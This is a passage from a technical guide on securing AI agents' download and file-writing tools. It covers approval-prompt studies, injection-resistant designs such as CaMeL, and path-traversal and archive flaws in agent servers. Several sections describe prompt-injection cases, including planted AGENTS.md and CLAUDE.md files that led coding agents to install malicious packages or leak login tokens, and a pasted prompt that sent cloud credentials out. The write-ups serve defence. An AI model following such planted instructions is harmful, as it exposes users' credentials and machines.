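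People pay less attention the more often a program asks for permission. Anthropic reports that users of Claude Code, its coding agent, approved about 93% of permission prompts and became less attentive as the prompts accumulated. The approval rate alone doesn't show carelessness, since most requests were probably legitimate. Experienced users auto-approved actions about twice as often as new users, but they also interrupted the agent more often while it was working.

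*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of incidents in which agents mishandled files. Problems with the user's review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31, the approval prompt didn't explain what the command would do. Some incidents involved both problems. Attackers may learn to exploit reviewers' fatigue. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) cites work in which Google DeepMind anticipates attacks designed to wear reviewers down or show them harmless-looking summaries.

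**Better prompts.** Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, measured how much the content of a prompt matters. They asked 80 volunteers to approve or deny actions that an agent proposed, half of which broke the user's original instructions. In one scenario, a user allowed the agent to send an auditor only summary totals, but the agent had built the attached file from raw invoice data several steps earlier. Each volunteer used one of four designs and made 12 decisions:

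| What the prompt showed | Unsafe actions approved | Legitimate actions approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The arguments, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, arranged to show the action's overall effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

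Showing more information accounts for most of the improvement. The gain from the last step, from the log to the summary of effects, is less certain. After statistical adjustment, the summary did 7.9 percentage points better, but the 95% interval ran from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse. Even with the best design, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe actions. They would probably do worse in daily use, where attacks are rare and people haven't just been asked to look for them.

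Standing rules might help, because users could decide once instead of every time. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested such rules with 113 people who weren't software professionals. One group set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something. The agent then worked through a simulated day in which 7 of its 18 actions went beyond what the user had requested.

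The rules reduced the average number of prompts from 18.0 to 10.9, but this group's rate of blocking excessive actions was 20 percentage points lower than that of people who approved every action individually. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and they usually approved the action when asked. People approved 133 of the 148 excessive actions that went ahead. Yan compared whole designs, so the study doesn't show exactly which feature caused the difference, and the agent was overstepping on its own, without an attacker. For downloads, the results suggest that an administrator should settle as many cases as possible with firm rules and keep "ask" for the few that need the user's knowledge.

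Approval also fails when someone has deceived the user. In an internal exercise at Anthropic, a researcher sent an employee a plausible email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt's setup steps included reading a file of cloud credentials and sending the contents to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. A rule that allows URLs from the user's message would have allowed that address too.

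**Approving the exact request.** The parse-once rule also applies to approvals, so the tool may run only the call the user saw. Hossain and colleagues recommend showing the user arguments taken from a trusted record instead of the agent's description. For `download_file`, the approval should cover the full URL and the destination, and the tool should use each approval only once. Approving `files.example.net` as a whole would let the next request send different data to the same server.

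A download tool should also wait for the user to answer the approval prompt before it makes any network request. Anthropic received reports of three flaws in Claude Code that let code run before the user had consented to anything. In one case, a project's settings could run an attacker's command before the program asked whether the user trusted the folder. A download tool makes the same mistake if it fetches a preview or looks up the hostname to fill in its approval prompt.

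### Planning before reading untrusted content

The rules so far apply to a call after the model has written it. A developer can also arrange the agent so that text from a web page never reaches the model that selects which tools to call. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six such arrangements. All of them follow the principle that untrusted text must not be able to trigger a harmful action once an agent has taken it in.

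In the plan-then-execute pattern, the model commits to a list of tool calls before it reads anything untrusted. The dual LLM pattern uses two models. A privileged model plans and can use tools but sees only the user's request, while a quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. Ordinary software passes the results between them as variables, so the privileged model can use a value without reading it.

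CaMeL, a system that Debenedetti and colleagues described in 2025, combines these ideas. The privileged model writes its plan as a small program, and an interpreter runs it. For the employee who pasted a link and wrote "Save this report and summarise it", the program could look like this:

```python
file = download_file(
    url="https://files.example.com/annual-report.pdf",
    destination="reports",
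)
text = read_file(file)
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise this report", text)
show_to_user(summary)
```

If the PDF contains an instruction to download something else, only the quarantined model reads it. That model can write a false summary, but it can't add a line to the program. The application still has to remove or check links and images in the summary before displaying it, because loading one could send data to an outside server.

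The plan gives less protection when the URL itself comes from untrusted text. Suppose the employee instead asks for the report that a supplier's page links to:

```python
page = fetch_page("https://supplier.example/reports")
link = quarantined_model("Find the link to the annual report", page)
download_file(url=link, destination="reports")
```

The page's author can't change the sequence of steps but can choose the value of `link`, so CaMeL also tracks data. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, explains that the interpreter labels each value with its sources and the readers who may see it. Before every tool call, a policy written in ordinary code checks the arguments and their labels, then allows or denies the call.

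For a URL built from the values $v_1, \ldots, v_k$, a cautious policy would combine the labels like this:

$$\mathrm{Sources}(u) = \bigcup_{i=1}^{k} \mathrm{Sources}(v_i) \qquad \mathrm{Readers}(u) = \bigcap_{i=1}^{k} \mathrm{Readers}(v_i)$$

The URL then counts as coming from every source that contributed to it, and only someone who may read all of its parts may read the whole. A fetch reveals the URL to the server, so the policy allows the download only if the server may read the URL. The link from the supplier's page contains nothing private, so the policy allows it. A URL that includes the project's name takes on the restrictions of the internal notes, so the policy blocks the request to `files.example.net`.

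Labels can catch leaks that a text filter would miss. Lan and colleagues propose, but did not test, a similar kind of tracking that would mark text from web pages as untrusted and pass that mark to any tool argument the text influenced. The tool could then block a request prompted by a web page, even if the request carried only a harmless-looking four-character piece of a key. Labels on private data could help against Paul's attack. If the model that picked each link had also read the user's private details, and its output inherited the labels of everything it read, the policy would treat the choice of link as private too.

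This caution can interrupt harmless downloads. If a model reads one confidential note along with twenty public pages, all of its output may be treated as confidential, and the agent then has to stop or ask the user. Planning in advance also works badly for some tasks. If a user says "follow the installation instructions on this page", the right steps depend on text that the planner isn't supposed to read.

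Results so far are encouraging. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all the injection attacks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of office-style tasks, with comparable task performance. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) calls the loss of completed tasks comparatively modest and expects it to shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. It is less clear how well such designs handle open-ended work. *AgentDyn* (2026) provides a benchmark for this, but acknowledges that its attacks are relatively weak against the newest models.

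Hossain and colleagues tested adding data tracking to an ordinary agent. Their monitor records which files the agent built from which inputs, and compares each proposed action with the user's instructions. It detected 89.2% of 120 violations. When the researchers let it block actions, the share of runs in which one agent caused a forbidden effect fell from 43.3% to 5.0%, and the agent completed slightly fewer legitimate tasks. Better approval prompts for human reviewers achieved a much smaller reduction, although the two experiments measured different things. The monitor also blocks an action when its records are incomplete, so its usefulness depends on how many of the agent's tools it can observe.

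Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable safety guarantees, and recommend building agents for narrower jobs. Their planning patterns also rely on the user's message being trustworthy, so the patterns don't protect an employee who pastes a link from a phishing email.

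## Choosing where the file is written

Once a download tool has a permitted address, it needs a path for the file. The stricter schema for download_file lets the model pick one of two folders, and ordinary code sets the file name. Strangers control most of the convenient sources for that name.

Path traversal, in which a name or path leads outside the intended folder, was among the most common flaws that Ananto and colleagues found in MCP servers. In their tests, one server deleted files outside its workspace, and another followed a path out of its notes folder.

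### Who supplies the file name

| Source of the name | Who can choose it |
|---|---|
| The user's message | The user, or whoever wrote the text that the user copied |
| The `destination` argument | The model, and anyone whose text the model has read |
| The last part of the URL | Whoever wrote the link |
| The URL after a redirect | Whoever runs the server that sent the redirect |
| The Content-Disposition header | Whoever runs the server that sent the file |
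| An entry in an archive | Whoever made the archive |

A server can suggest a file name in the Content-Disposition response header. *Trusting the Filename* (2026), a study of three recent flaws, points out that applications treat such names as if they had chosen the names themselves, even though an attacker may have chosen them.

Crawl4AI, the crawler that PraisonAI's web_crawl could use, took the file name from this header and joined it to its downloads folder without checking the result. Corgea's *Crawl4AI* explains that an attacker could therefore choose both a file's contents and where it was written on the disk. Aikido, a security firm, found the same mistake in browser-use, a library that lets agents operate a browser. An attacker only needed the agent to visit a malicious site. Version 0.12.7 fixed the flaw.

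Some sources of file paths are easier to overlook. Spring's *Arbitrary File Write via Path Traversal in ResourceCacheService* (2026) describes a cache for downloaded AI models that built each file name partly from the URL's fragment, the text after a `#`. HTTP clients don't send the fragment to the server, so the attack wouldn't show up in a log of network requests. VulnCheck's *BlenderMCP Path Traversal via download_polyhaven_asset API* reports that BlenderMCP, which connects agents to the 3D program Blender, took file paths from field names in an online library's response.

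### Tools that accept any path

Many tools don't check the path at all. The mcp-atlassian server gives agents access to Confluence, a wiki that companies use internally. Its attachment download tool accepted a full path from the model and wrote the file there, creating any missing folders. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-408* (2026) notes that the code called Python's `os.path.abspath`, which could be mistaken for a safety check in a quick review. That function only turns a relative path into a full one and doesn't compare it with a permitted folder.

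An attacker who uploaded an attachment and chose where it was saved could put a file where the system's scheduler would run it within a minute. The server required no password by default, so anyone who could reach it over the network could call the tool. An attacker could also get an agent to call it by writing instructions into a Confluence page. Version 0.17.0 fixed the flaw.

browse-mcp, a browser server for agents, let the caller choose the folder in the same way until version 0.8.2. OSV's *CVE-2026-55557* (2026) adds that a fallback in the server ignored its list of allowed sites, so the attacker could also choose freely where the file came from.

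Flowise, a visual tool for building agents, had a file-writing tool that took an argument described as "name of file". Corgea's *Flowise is vulnerable to arbitrary file write through its WriteFileTool* shows from the code that the tool did not check whether the value was inside the working folder before passing it on. To exploit this flaw, CVE-2025-61913, an attacker needed an account on the Flowise server. The fix has to confine the path to a narrow working folder. The published test set the tool's base folder to the root of the disk, where even a perfect containment check would allow every path.

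AutoGPT had a similar flaw in 2023. Its `execute_python_code` command ran the model's code inside a container, an environment isolated from the rest of the machine, but first saved the code under a name the model also supplied. According to OSV's *CVE-2023-37274* (2023), the command didn't check that name. A name containing `..`, which stands for the parent folder, could lead out of the workspace and overwrite other Python files. One possible target was AutoGPT's own main program, which would run outside the container the next time the user started it. Version 0.4.3 fixed this. AutoGPT's `download_file` command did check its file name, so the flaw came from writing files in more than one place.

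Approval settings don't replace a path check in the code that writes the file. In October 2025 the security firm HiddenLayer got Windsurf, an AI code editor, to read a file outside the user's project and then overwrite it. HiddenLayer's *Path Traversal in File Tools Allowing Arbitrary Filesystem Access* (2025) reports that this worked in version 1.12.12 and earlier, even with automatic execution off and the writing tool on the deny list. In September 2026 the firm reported that Mistral Vibe, a coding agent, automatically approved many shell commands without applying its workspace restrictions to them.

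### A check that passes and a check that refuses

A tool that does check the path can still compare it in the wrong way. Suppose an agent may write only in `/srv/agent/work`, and a call names a file in a neighbouring folder, `/srv/agent/work-private`. Here are two possible checks in Python:

```python
from pathlib import Path

folder = "/srv/agent/work"
path = "/srv/agent/work-private/report.pdf"

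path.startswith(folder)                                     # True
Path(path).resolve().is_relative_to(Path(folder).resolve()) # False
```

The first check compares characters. The path begins with the same 15 characters as the folder, so the check accepts it. The second check resolves both paths, which means removing `..` parts and following links, and then compares them folder by folder. If the resolved folder has the parts $r_1, \ldots, r_n$ and the resolved path has the parts $p_1, \ldots, p_m$, the path lies inside the folder only when

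$$m \geq n \quad \text{and} \quad p_i = r_i \text{ for every } i \leq n$$

In the example, $r_3$ is `work` and $p_3$ is `work-private`, so the second check refuses the path. The two checks also differ on other paths:

| Path | What it resolves to | Prefix check | Resolved-path check |
|---|---|---|---|
| `/srv/agent/work/report.pdf` | The same path | Accepts | Accepts |
| `/srv/agent/work-private/report.pdf` | The same path | Accepts | Refuses |
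| `/srv/agent/work/../notes.txt` | `/srv/agent/notes.txt` | Accepts | Refuses |
| `/srv/agent/work/latest.pdf`, a link to `/home/ana/thesis.pdf` | `/home/ana/thesis.pdf` | Accepts | Refuses |

Adding a slash to the end of the folder's name would fix the prefix check for the second row but not for the last two.

Anthropic's Filesystem MCP server, a reference implementation that other developers copy and extend, used a prefix check. In *EscapeRoute*, Beber showed that an agent limited to one folder could list, read and write in any neighbouring folder whose name began with the allowed folder's name. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Filesystem MCP Server* reports that Johann Rehberger found the flaw independently. Beber reported it on 30 March 2025, and Anthropic fixed it three months later in version 2025.7.1. The vulnerable version removed `..` parts before comparing paths, so it would have refused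 the path in the third row.

The order of the steps matters too. PraisonAI's file tools also removed `..` parts first, but then searched the result for `..` as a sign of attack. OSV's *GHSA-693f-pf34-72c5* explains that the search came too late to find anything. A path such as `/srv/agent/work/../notes.txt` had already become `/srv/agent/notes.txt`, which is outside `work` but contains no `..`. Searching for `..` also can't catch an absolute path to a location outside the permitted folder. Joining that path to the permitted folder doesn't help, because Python's `os.path.join` discards the folder when the second part is absolute. GCVE (2026), a vulnerability catalogue, lists 1.5.113 as the fixed version.

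Similar flaws keep appearing in file servers for agents. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-7400* (2026) describes a server whose `is_path_allowed` function let disallowed paths through until version 1.1.0. Kandhare's *claude-faf-mcp Arbitrary File Read/Write via Unconfined Path Argument* (2026) describes another that resolved paths but never checked whether they were inside an allowed folder. Version 5.7.2 fixed that flaw in August.

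### Symbolic links

A symbolic link is an entry in a folder that points to another path. When a program opens the link, the operating system normally opens the target, which can be anywhere on the disk. An ordinary download doesn't create links, but archives and code repositories can contain them.

Anthropic's server did resolve links before it accepted a path, but its error handling undid the check. In outline, the code worked like this:

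```
try:
    resolve the path
    if it leads outside the folder, raise an error
    accept the resolved path
if any error occurs:
    check the parent folder of the original path
    if that is inside, accept the original path
```

The second half of the check was for new files, which the server couldn't resolve because they didn't exist yet. But a link that led outside the allowed folders also raised an error, so the server went on to check the folder containing the link. That folder passed, so the server opened the link despite having first rejected it. Beber used this flaw, CVE-2025-53109, to write a settings file that made macOS start a program at the next login. During the tests, Claude suggested that its use of a folder missing from its list might be a security flaw, but only after it had accessed the folder.

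The fallback should run only when the file doesn't exist, and even then a link can redirect the write. cMCP, a project for testing MCP servers, set up a link to an outside file that didn't exist yet. When the agent wrote to the link, the server created the outside file. The tool therefore has to check whether the last part of the path is itself a link, and refuse it if so, whether or not the target exists.

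Links can also let a program read files outside the permitted area. Openwall's *Vulnerability report* (2026) describes a file server that checked for links only at the top of a search. The search then entered linked subfolders and returned text from files outside that area.

### Paths that change after the check

Even a correct path check can be out of date by the time the file is written. If another program replaces a folder in the path with a link after the check but before the write, the file goes wherever the link points. DNS rebinding exploits the same kind of gap between checking an address and connecting to it.

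OpenClaw, an open-source agent that people run on their own computers, had a race condition in how it unpacked ZIP archives. Wiz's *CVE-2026-27670* explains that the code checked each output path and opened the file in a separate step. An attacker who could already change folders on the machine could swap a folder between the two steps. Because the attacker needs that access, the flaw is less urgent than a server that accepts any path, and it is rated medium severity. Testers can easily miss it, though. Ananto and colleagues acknowledge that fuzzing with single inputs is poorly suited to finding such races.

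OpenClaw's browser tool had a related flaw, and version 2026.3.2 fixed both. According to GitLab's *GHSA-3pxq-f3cp-jmxp* (2026), the new code uses the operating system's handle to verify the file it has opened. The handle keeps referring to that file even if someone later changes the path.

### Overwriting and names that match unexpectedly

Even in the right folder, a download can overwrite an existing file with the same name. Checking first whether the name is free again leaves a gap between the check and the write, so the tool should have the operating system create the file only if nothing exists at that path.

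This also avoids having to decide when two names are the same. By default, Windows and macOS treat `Report.pdf` and `report.pdf` as one file, but a simple string comparison treats them as different. Unicode also allows é to be written as either one character or an e followed by a separate accent. macOS normally treats the two spellings as the same name, while Linux usually treats them as different. A tool that checks new names against its own list could therefore miss a match and overwrite an existing file. A rule that protects `.env`, a file where developers often keep passwords, could also miss `.ENV`.

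### Archives

Unpacking an archive turns one download into many writes. Each entry in a ZIP or tar file has its own path, and some entries are links. Whoever made the archive chose those paths, even if the tool chose a safe place for the archive itself.

*Your Agent May Misevolve* describes an agent that created this problem for itself. A user asked for a way to extract a tar file into a given folder, and the agent wrote a tool around `extractall`, a function in Python's standard library. When the user later asked it to extract another archive, which contained an entry for `/etc/passwd`, the system's list of user accounts, the agent reused the tool without looking at the entries. The paper attributes the mistake to the agent's assumption that the library function was safe by default.

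Across the study's pairs of tasks, the tool itself was unsafe in an average of 34.5% of cases. In another 31%, the tool was sound but the agent used it unsafely. Scanning new tools for flaws would therefore address only about half of the unsafe cases. The researchers suggest a second review whenever an agent reuses a tool, but didn't test this.

The same Python code is safer on newer versions. GCVE (2025) notes that Python 3.14 changed the default from no filtering to a filter called "data", which should keep entries inside the destination. Attackers have found ways past this filter too. The GCVE entry covers one bypass, and Ulbrych (2026) announced another in June 2026 in *tarfile.data_filter path traversal bypass allows writing outside the extraction directory*. The newer one used specially made links to redirect entries later in the archive. Each path can look harmless on its own, because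 the danger comes from the order in which the tool writes the entries.

OpenClaw also had to fix its archive code several times. Before version 2026.2.14, it accepted tar entries with `..` in their paths, according to GitLab's *GHSA-p25h-9q54-ffvw* (2026). Endor Labs describes a later fix for ZIP files, needed because a check looked only at the text of each path and missed links already in the destination. *Trusting the Filename* reports that Malcolm, a network-monitoring program, checked the paths of files but not those of folders.

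A download tool is safest when it saves archives without unpacking them. If the agent needs the contents, the tool should extract them into a new, empty folder, so there are no existing links to follow. It should refuse every entry that isn't an ordinary file or folder, and apply the resolved-path check to each remaining entry just before writing it. Refusing links will break some software packages that use them legitimately, but archives of reports and spreadsheets rarely need them. The tool also needs size limits, because a small archive can expand enormously.

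### Writing the file safely

A download tool can avoid most of these problems by never using a stranger's text as a path. In order, it should:

1. Generate the stored name itself, from random characters and an extension on a fixed list.
2. Keep the original name only as a label, in a database or a separate record.
3. Write to a new temporary file in a dedicated folder that other programs can't change.
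4. Open that file without following links.
5. Refuse to overwrite anything.
6. Give the file no execute permission.
7. Move the file to its final folder only after every check has passed, again without overwriting.

On Linux or macOS, the core of a tool that saves PDFs could look like this:

```python
import os, secrets

NEW_FILE = os.O_WRONLY | os.O_CREAT | os.O_EXCL | os.O_NOFOLLOW

def save(chunks, original_name, incoming, final):
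    name = secrets.token_hex(16) + ".pdf"
    handle = os.open(name, NEW_FILE, mode=0o600, dir_fd=incoming)
    try:
        with os.fdopen(handle, "wb") as file:
            for chunk in chunks:
                file.write(chunk)
        check_file(name, incoming)
        os.link(name, name, src_dir_fd=incoming, dst_dir_fd=final)
    finally:
        os.unlink(name, dir_fd=incoming)
    save_label(name, original_name)
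    return name
```

Here `incoming` and `final` are handles to two folders that the tool opened when it started. `O_NOFOLLOW` checks only the last part of a path, but the tool passes a bare file name with a folder handle, so there are no earlier parts for an attacker to swap. `O_EXCL` makes the call fail if the name already exists, even as a link. The mode `0o600` lets the tool's own account read and write the file, but nobody can execute it directly. An interpreter such as Python can still run a script it can read, so this permission is a modest safeguard.

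An ordinary rename on these systems silently replaces an existing file, so the tool uses `os.link` for the last step. This gives the finished file a second name in the final folder and fails if that name already exists. The tool then removes the temporary name. Both folders have to be on the same disk. If a check fails or the connection breaks, the tool deletes the partial file and nothing appears in the final folder.

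People find a name like `annual-report.pdf` easier to use than a random one. The tool can show the label in its interface, or build a readable filename from the label's plain letters and digits, converted to lower case, with a few random characters at the end. The label is still untrusted text, so the tool should remove control characters before displaying it and shouldn't return it to the model unless the task requires it.

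A coding agent often has to write to a particular path in a project, so it can't use generated names. Its write function has to keep files inside the allowed folder instead. Recent versions of Linux have a system call, `openat2`, that can reject any path leading out of a given folder as it opens the file, which leaves no gap between the check and the write.

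## What a saved file can do afterwards

A download tool can fetch a file from a permitted address, write it to the right folder, and still leave something harmful on the disk. A person or an agent may run the file if it is a script or an installer. Opening the file may exploit a flaw in the program that reads it or run active content, such as a spreadsheet macro. An agent may read the file and follow instructions in its text.

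Operating systems and virus scanners mainly look for harmful programs, so they offer little protection against a text file that does nothing until an agent reads it.

### The AGENTS.md file in a Downloads folder

Forever Security, a firm that monitors AI agents on its customers' computers, stopped a customer's coding agent from installing a malicious package called function-color. The package was on npm, the main public library of JavaScript code, and belonged to a campaign that had gone unnoticed for about two years. The instruction to install it came from a text file named AGENTS.md in the customer's Downloads folder, where the agent was working. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* reports that the instruction's source led the researchers, Gal Weizman and Omer Samet, to investigate. Mynavi News' *CodexとClaude Codeに攻撃の恐れ、悪意ある指示ファイルで不正コード実行*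 (2026) dates the firm's report, *Markdown Is the New Executable*, to 22 October 2026.

Developers put an AGENTS.md file in a project to tell coding agents which tools to use and how to run the tests. Claude Code's equivalent is CLAUDE.md. Agents load these files automatically and trust them, which NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* describes as deliberate. Prompt Security's *When your repo starts talking* points out that the AGENTS.md specification has no security model and no guidance for programs that load an untrusted copy.

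Nobody established how the file reached the customer's computer, but a website could have put it there. Chrome, Edge and Firefox save downloads to this folder without asking where each one should go, and a page can start a download by itself. On Forever's test page, the browser saved the file as the visitor left. Clubic's *Codex et Claude Code peuvent être piégés par un fichier* says that the news site BleepingComputer tried a demonstration and received a harmless file. Playtech's *Un simplu fișier descărcat de pe internet poate transforma ChatGPT Codex* explains that whether the user notices depends on the browser and its settings.

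The agent can also download the file itself if it visits a malicious page. About half of the customers of Forever, a security firm, run a coding agent in the Downloads folder at least sometimes, and about a quarter of agent sessions open a browser. These figures cover only Forever's customers, so they may not hold for developers in general.

The researchers tested the customer's file on OpenAI's Codex. Codex ignores such files in folders it doesn't trust, but it treats Downloads as trusted after the user has done some work there. When the researchers started Codex in Downloads with an arbitrary task, it first added a new tool server to its own settings and installed the package. This worked in more than 90% of attempts. Most of the tests replaced the package with a harmless one that opened a calculator, and the researchers ran the real package only once, in an isolated virtual machine. The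 changed settings applied to the whole computer, so later Codex sessions ran the attacker's command in every project.

The file was 13 KB long and resembled ordinary engineering guidelines. Codex refused a short request to install a package, so the length and dull tone were part of the attack.

Claude Code was harder to fool, so the researchers wrote a different file for it. Their CLAUDE.md asked for a small settings change that sent Claude Code's requests to a server they controlled, which the file presented as a company's internal gateway. Claude made the change in about 50% of tests. Each request carried the user's login token, which the researchers used to take over the account. The next time Claude Code started in that folder, their server could also pose as the model and send back commands to run. In about 20% of tests, they ran code within the first session by getting Claude Code to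 start a helper agent.

The 90% and 50% figures show that this kind of attack works on more than one company's agent. They can't be used to rank the two products, because one attack installed a package and the other redirected network traffic.

Forever argues that OpenAI and Anthropic have nothing to patch, because an agent that follows the instruction file in its folder is working as designed. According to Clubic, both companies advise users to start agents from the project's folder, never from Downloads, and to keep approvals and the sandbox on. Codex trusts the whole folder, including files that arrive later, but an agent could instead be designed to ask the user before it follows a new or changed instruction file.

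OpenAI had already considered a related attack, in which a malicious code library created by NVIDIA wrote an AGENTS.md file during a build. Codex then added a five-minute delay to the user's program and left the delay out of its summary. OpenAI replied that this added no significant risk beyond that of a compromised library. That answer is reasonable when the attacker can already run code on the machine, but it doesn't fit the Downloads case, where the attacker starts with only a text file.

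The random file names recommended in the previous section would block the simplest version of this attack, because an agent looks for the exact name AGENTS.md. But files unpacked from an archive or copied with a code repository would keep their original names, so one of them could still be called AGENTS.md.

### Install instructions for packages nobody owned

An agent can also run harmful code by following instructions written in good faith. Many websites publish a file called llms.txt, which summarises their documentation for AI agents and often includes installation commands. Researchers at Pandex, an Israeli startup, looked for commands that named a package or web domain nobody had registered. Anyone could register such a name and decide what the command would install.

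The researchers scanned 6,214 domains of defence contractors, Fortune 500 companies and large technology firms. Schneier (2026), in *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks*, quotes a count of 8,265 files. Of these, 120, each on a different site, pointed to at least one unclaimed name. Ars Technica's *Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed unowned code inside corporate networks* (2026) counts 227 install commands that pointed to unclaimed names. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* gives 8,565 files and 237 references. On either file count, about one in seventy files pointed to an unclaimed name.

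The researchers then registered a handful of the names and uploaded packages that did nothing except contact the researchers' server when run. The first contact came after four minutes, and one from a Fortune 500 company came within an hour. A few dozen more followed from other large companies and startups. The packages also recorded which programs had started the installation, including Claude, Codex and Hermes, an agent from Nous Research. The companies that make these three programs did not respond to requests for comment.

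In a separate test, the researchers asked models to build and run a project using a vendor's documentation, without mentioning llms.txt or including a link. GPT-5 Luna and Sol ran the planted package at least 90% of the time, while Claude Opus 4.8 on medium effort ran it 30% of the time. Tom's Hardware reports that more autonomous models generally did worse. A model that searches the documentation thoroughly and sets up the project without help has more chances to find and run the command.

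Training against prompt injection may not help much here, because the instruction came from the real vendor and nobody wrote it to deceive. The danger began when somebody else claimed the name. Mondo's *Popularni AI agenti uhvaćeni u opasnom propustu* describes a similar case involving real malware. A command in clerk.com's llms.txt file named an unregistered package, and someone registered the name and used it to distribute the malware. Clerk later fixed the file, and it is unclear whether anyone was infected.

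The checks in download_file don't apply to these installations, because a package manager fetches the code. A domain allowlist may not stop them either, since a coding agent usually needs access to the main package registries. Installing a package can run its code. Microsoft's *33 malicious npm packages abuse dependency confusion* (2026) describes packages whose code ran during installation, before any program used them.

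A company can reduce the risk by letting agents install only approved packages, at fixed versions, from an internal collection. Turning off install scripts also helps, although a malicious package's code can still run when a program loads it.

### Reviewing a file can run it

A cautious user might ask an agent to inspect downloaded code before running it, but this can go wrong. *Exploit Brief*, by the research organisation AI Now Institute, describes an attack that targets Claude Code and Codex when developers use them to look for security flaws.

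The researchers added a few files to a copy of geopy, a Python library for looking up map coordinates. A note in its README, the file that introduces a project, recommended running a security script. The script started a program that the researchers had disguised as the compiled version of a harmless source file beside it. When a user asked for security testing, the agent read the note and ran the script.

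According to The Hacker News' *Top AI Agents Built to Catch Malicious Code Can Be Tricked* (2026), the same files worked on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Sonnet 5, Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5. In some runs, the newer models detected that the program didn't match its supposed source but ran it anyway. The attack worked only in an optional mode where the agent approves commands it classifies as safe.

AI Now argues that a model update can't fix this, but testing one set of files on four models is weak evidence for such a broad claim, and other kinds of injection have become much rarer in newer models. Whether or not AI Now is right, an agent that reviews untrusted code shouldn't be able to run it on a machine that matters.

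### Files that act when a program opens them

Some formats contain code that a program runs as part of opening, loading or installing the file:

| Format | How it can run code | Safer choice |
|---|---|---|
| Office files with macros, such as `.docm` and `.xlsm` | Word or Excel runs the macro if the user or a setting allows it | `.docx`, `.xlsx` or CSV, read with a library that doesn't run macros |
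| Installers | The installer runs the publisher's code, often with administrator rights | An approved package at a fixed version, installed in a sandbox |
| Model files in Python's pickle format | Loading the file can call functions that it names | The safetensors format |
| HTML pages | A browser runs the scripts in the page | Plain text that a separate program extracts |
| Project folders with hidden settings | An editor, an agent or Git runs commands from the settings | The source files without the settings |

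Even a format with no active content, such as a simple image, can exploit a bug in the program that reads it.

Loading an untrusted model file in Python's pickle format is equivalent to running an untrusted program. Pickle stores an object as a series of steps for rebuilding it, and a step can call a function with arguments chosen by the file's author. Since version 2.6, PyTorch, a widely used machine-learning library, has by default refused functions outside an approved list. Earlier versions offered the same restriction as an option, but a flaw in it, CVE-2025-32434, let a crafted file run code anyway.

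Safetensors avoids the problem by storing only the numbers and a description of their layout. It doesn't protect a user who also runs Python code supplied with the model.

HTML files were a security problem in several coding assistants in 2026. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (2026) reports another Forever study, in which the attack began with a project disguised as a financial report. When the user asked the assistant to set up the project, the assistant offered a link to an HTML file in it. One click let the page read files across the disk, including login keys and saved passwords, and send them out.

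An ordinary browser stops a local page from reading the user's other files. The assistants had relaxed this rule to preview projects. Claude Desktop and Microsoft's VS Code limited the page to its project folder, but the limit didn't cover background scripts that the page started. Codex had no folder limit. As of 29 October, Codex and VS Code still had no fix.

Anthropic and Microsoft rejected Forever's reports because users first have to confirm that they trust the project. Weizman replied that an untrusted project is unusable in these tools, "so everyone just hits 'Trust'". However, Anthropic accepted a report that another firm, Noma Security, filed a day after Forever's.

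Archives can carry hidden settings too. The version-control program Git keeps a project's settings in a folder called `.git`, and those settings can name commands for Git to run. Cloning a project from a server doesn't copy the server's settings, but unpacking a ZIP file that contains a `.git` folder brings in whatever settings are in that folder. Expert Insights' *Hackers can get Claude Code, Cursor and other AI agents to hack* reports that Manifold Security used this method against several agents. Goose, Claude Code and Cursor had been patched before the firm published its findings, but Codex, Hermes Agent, Qwen Code and Grok Build were still vulnerable. A second method still worked on the patched version of Claude Code.

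Agents have their own settings files. ETN's *Tekoälyagentti voidaan kaapata projektitiedostolla* describes a since-fixed flaw that made Claude Code run a command from a project's settings as soon as it opened the folder. The user didn't have to open the settings file or approve the command.

### Why the usual warnings don't appear

When a person downloads a program with a browser, the browser marks the file with where it came from, so the operating system often asks for confirmation before running it. On Windows, the mark is a small hidden data stream attached to the file, called Zone.Identifier. On macOS, it is an attribute called com.apple.quarantine.

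The program that saves the file normally has to add this mark. Browsers do, but simple HTTP clients, such as Python's requests library and curl, usually don't. A file saved by an agent's own download tool may therefore look as if it was created on the computer.

Levi explains in *clawhub supply chain attack* that macOS Gatekeeper doesn't ask the user for permission to run a program that lacks the quarantine attribute. In that attack, malicious instructions for agents included a command to remove the attribute. An attacker doesn't need that command if the file was downloaded without the attribute. On Windows, Office blocks macros by default in files marked as coming from the internet, so a missing mark weakens that protection too.

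A download tool can add the mark itself. On Windows, it writes these two lines to the Zone.Identifier stream, where 3 stands for the internet:

```
[ZoneTransfer]
ZoneId=3
```

Marking downloaded files is worth doing on a computer where people will open them, but some archive programs don't pass the mark on to the files they extract, and Linux has no equivalent that programs generally act on. An interpreter such as Python will usually run a marked script without asking for confirmation.

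The mark also makes no difference to AGENTS.md, because reading a text file doesn't trigger a warning. Developers could make an agent check for the mark and refuse to load instructions from files that came from the internet.

### What checks on a file can establish

The `save` function in the previous section left the inspection of each download to `check_file`, which for PDFs could begin like this:

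```python
def check_file(name, incoming):
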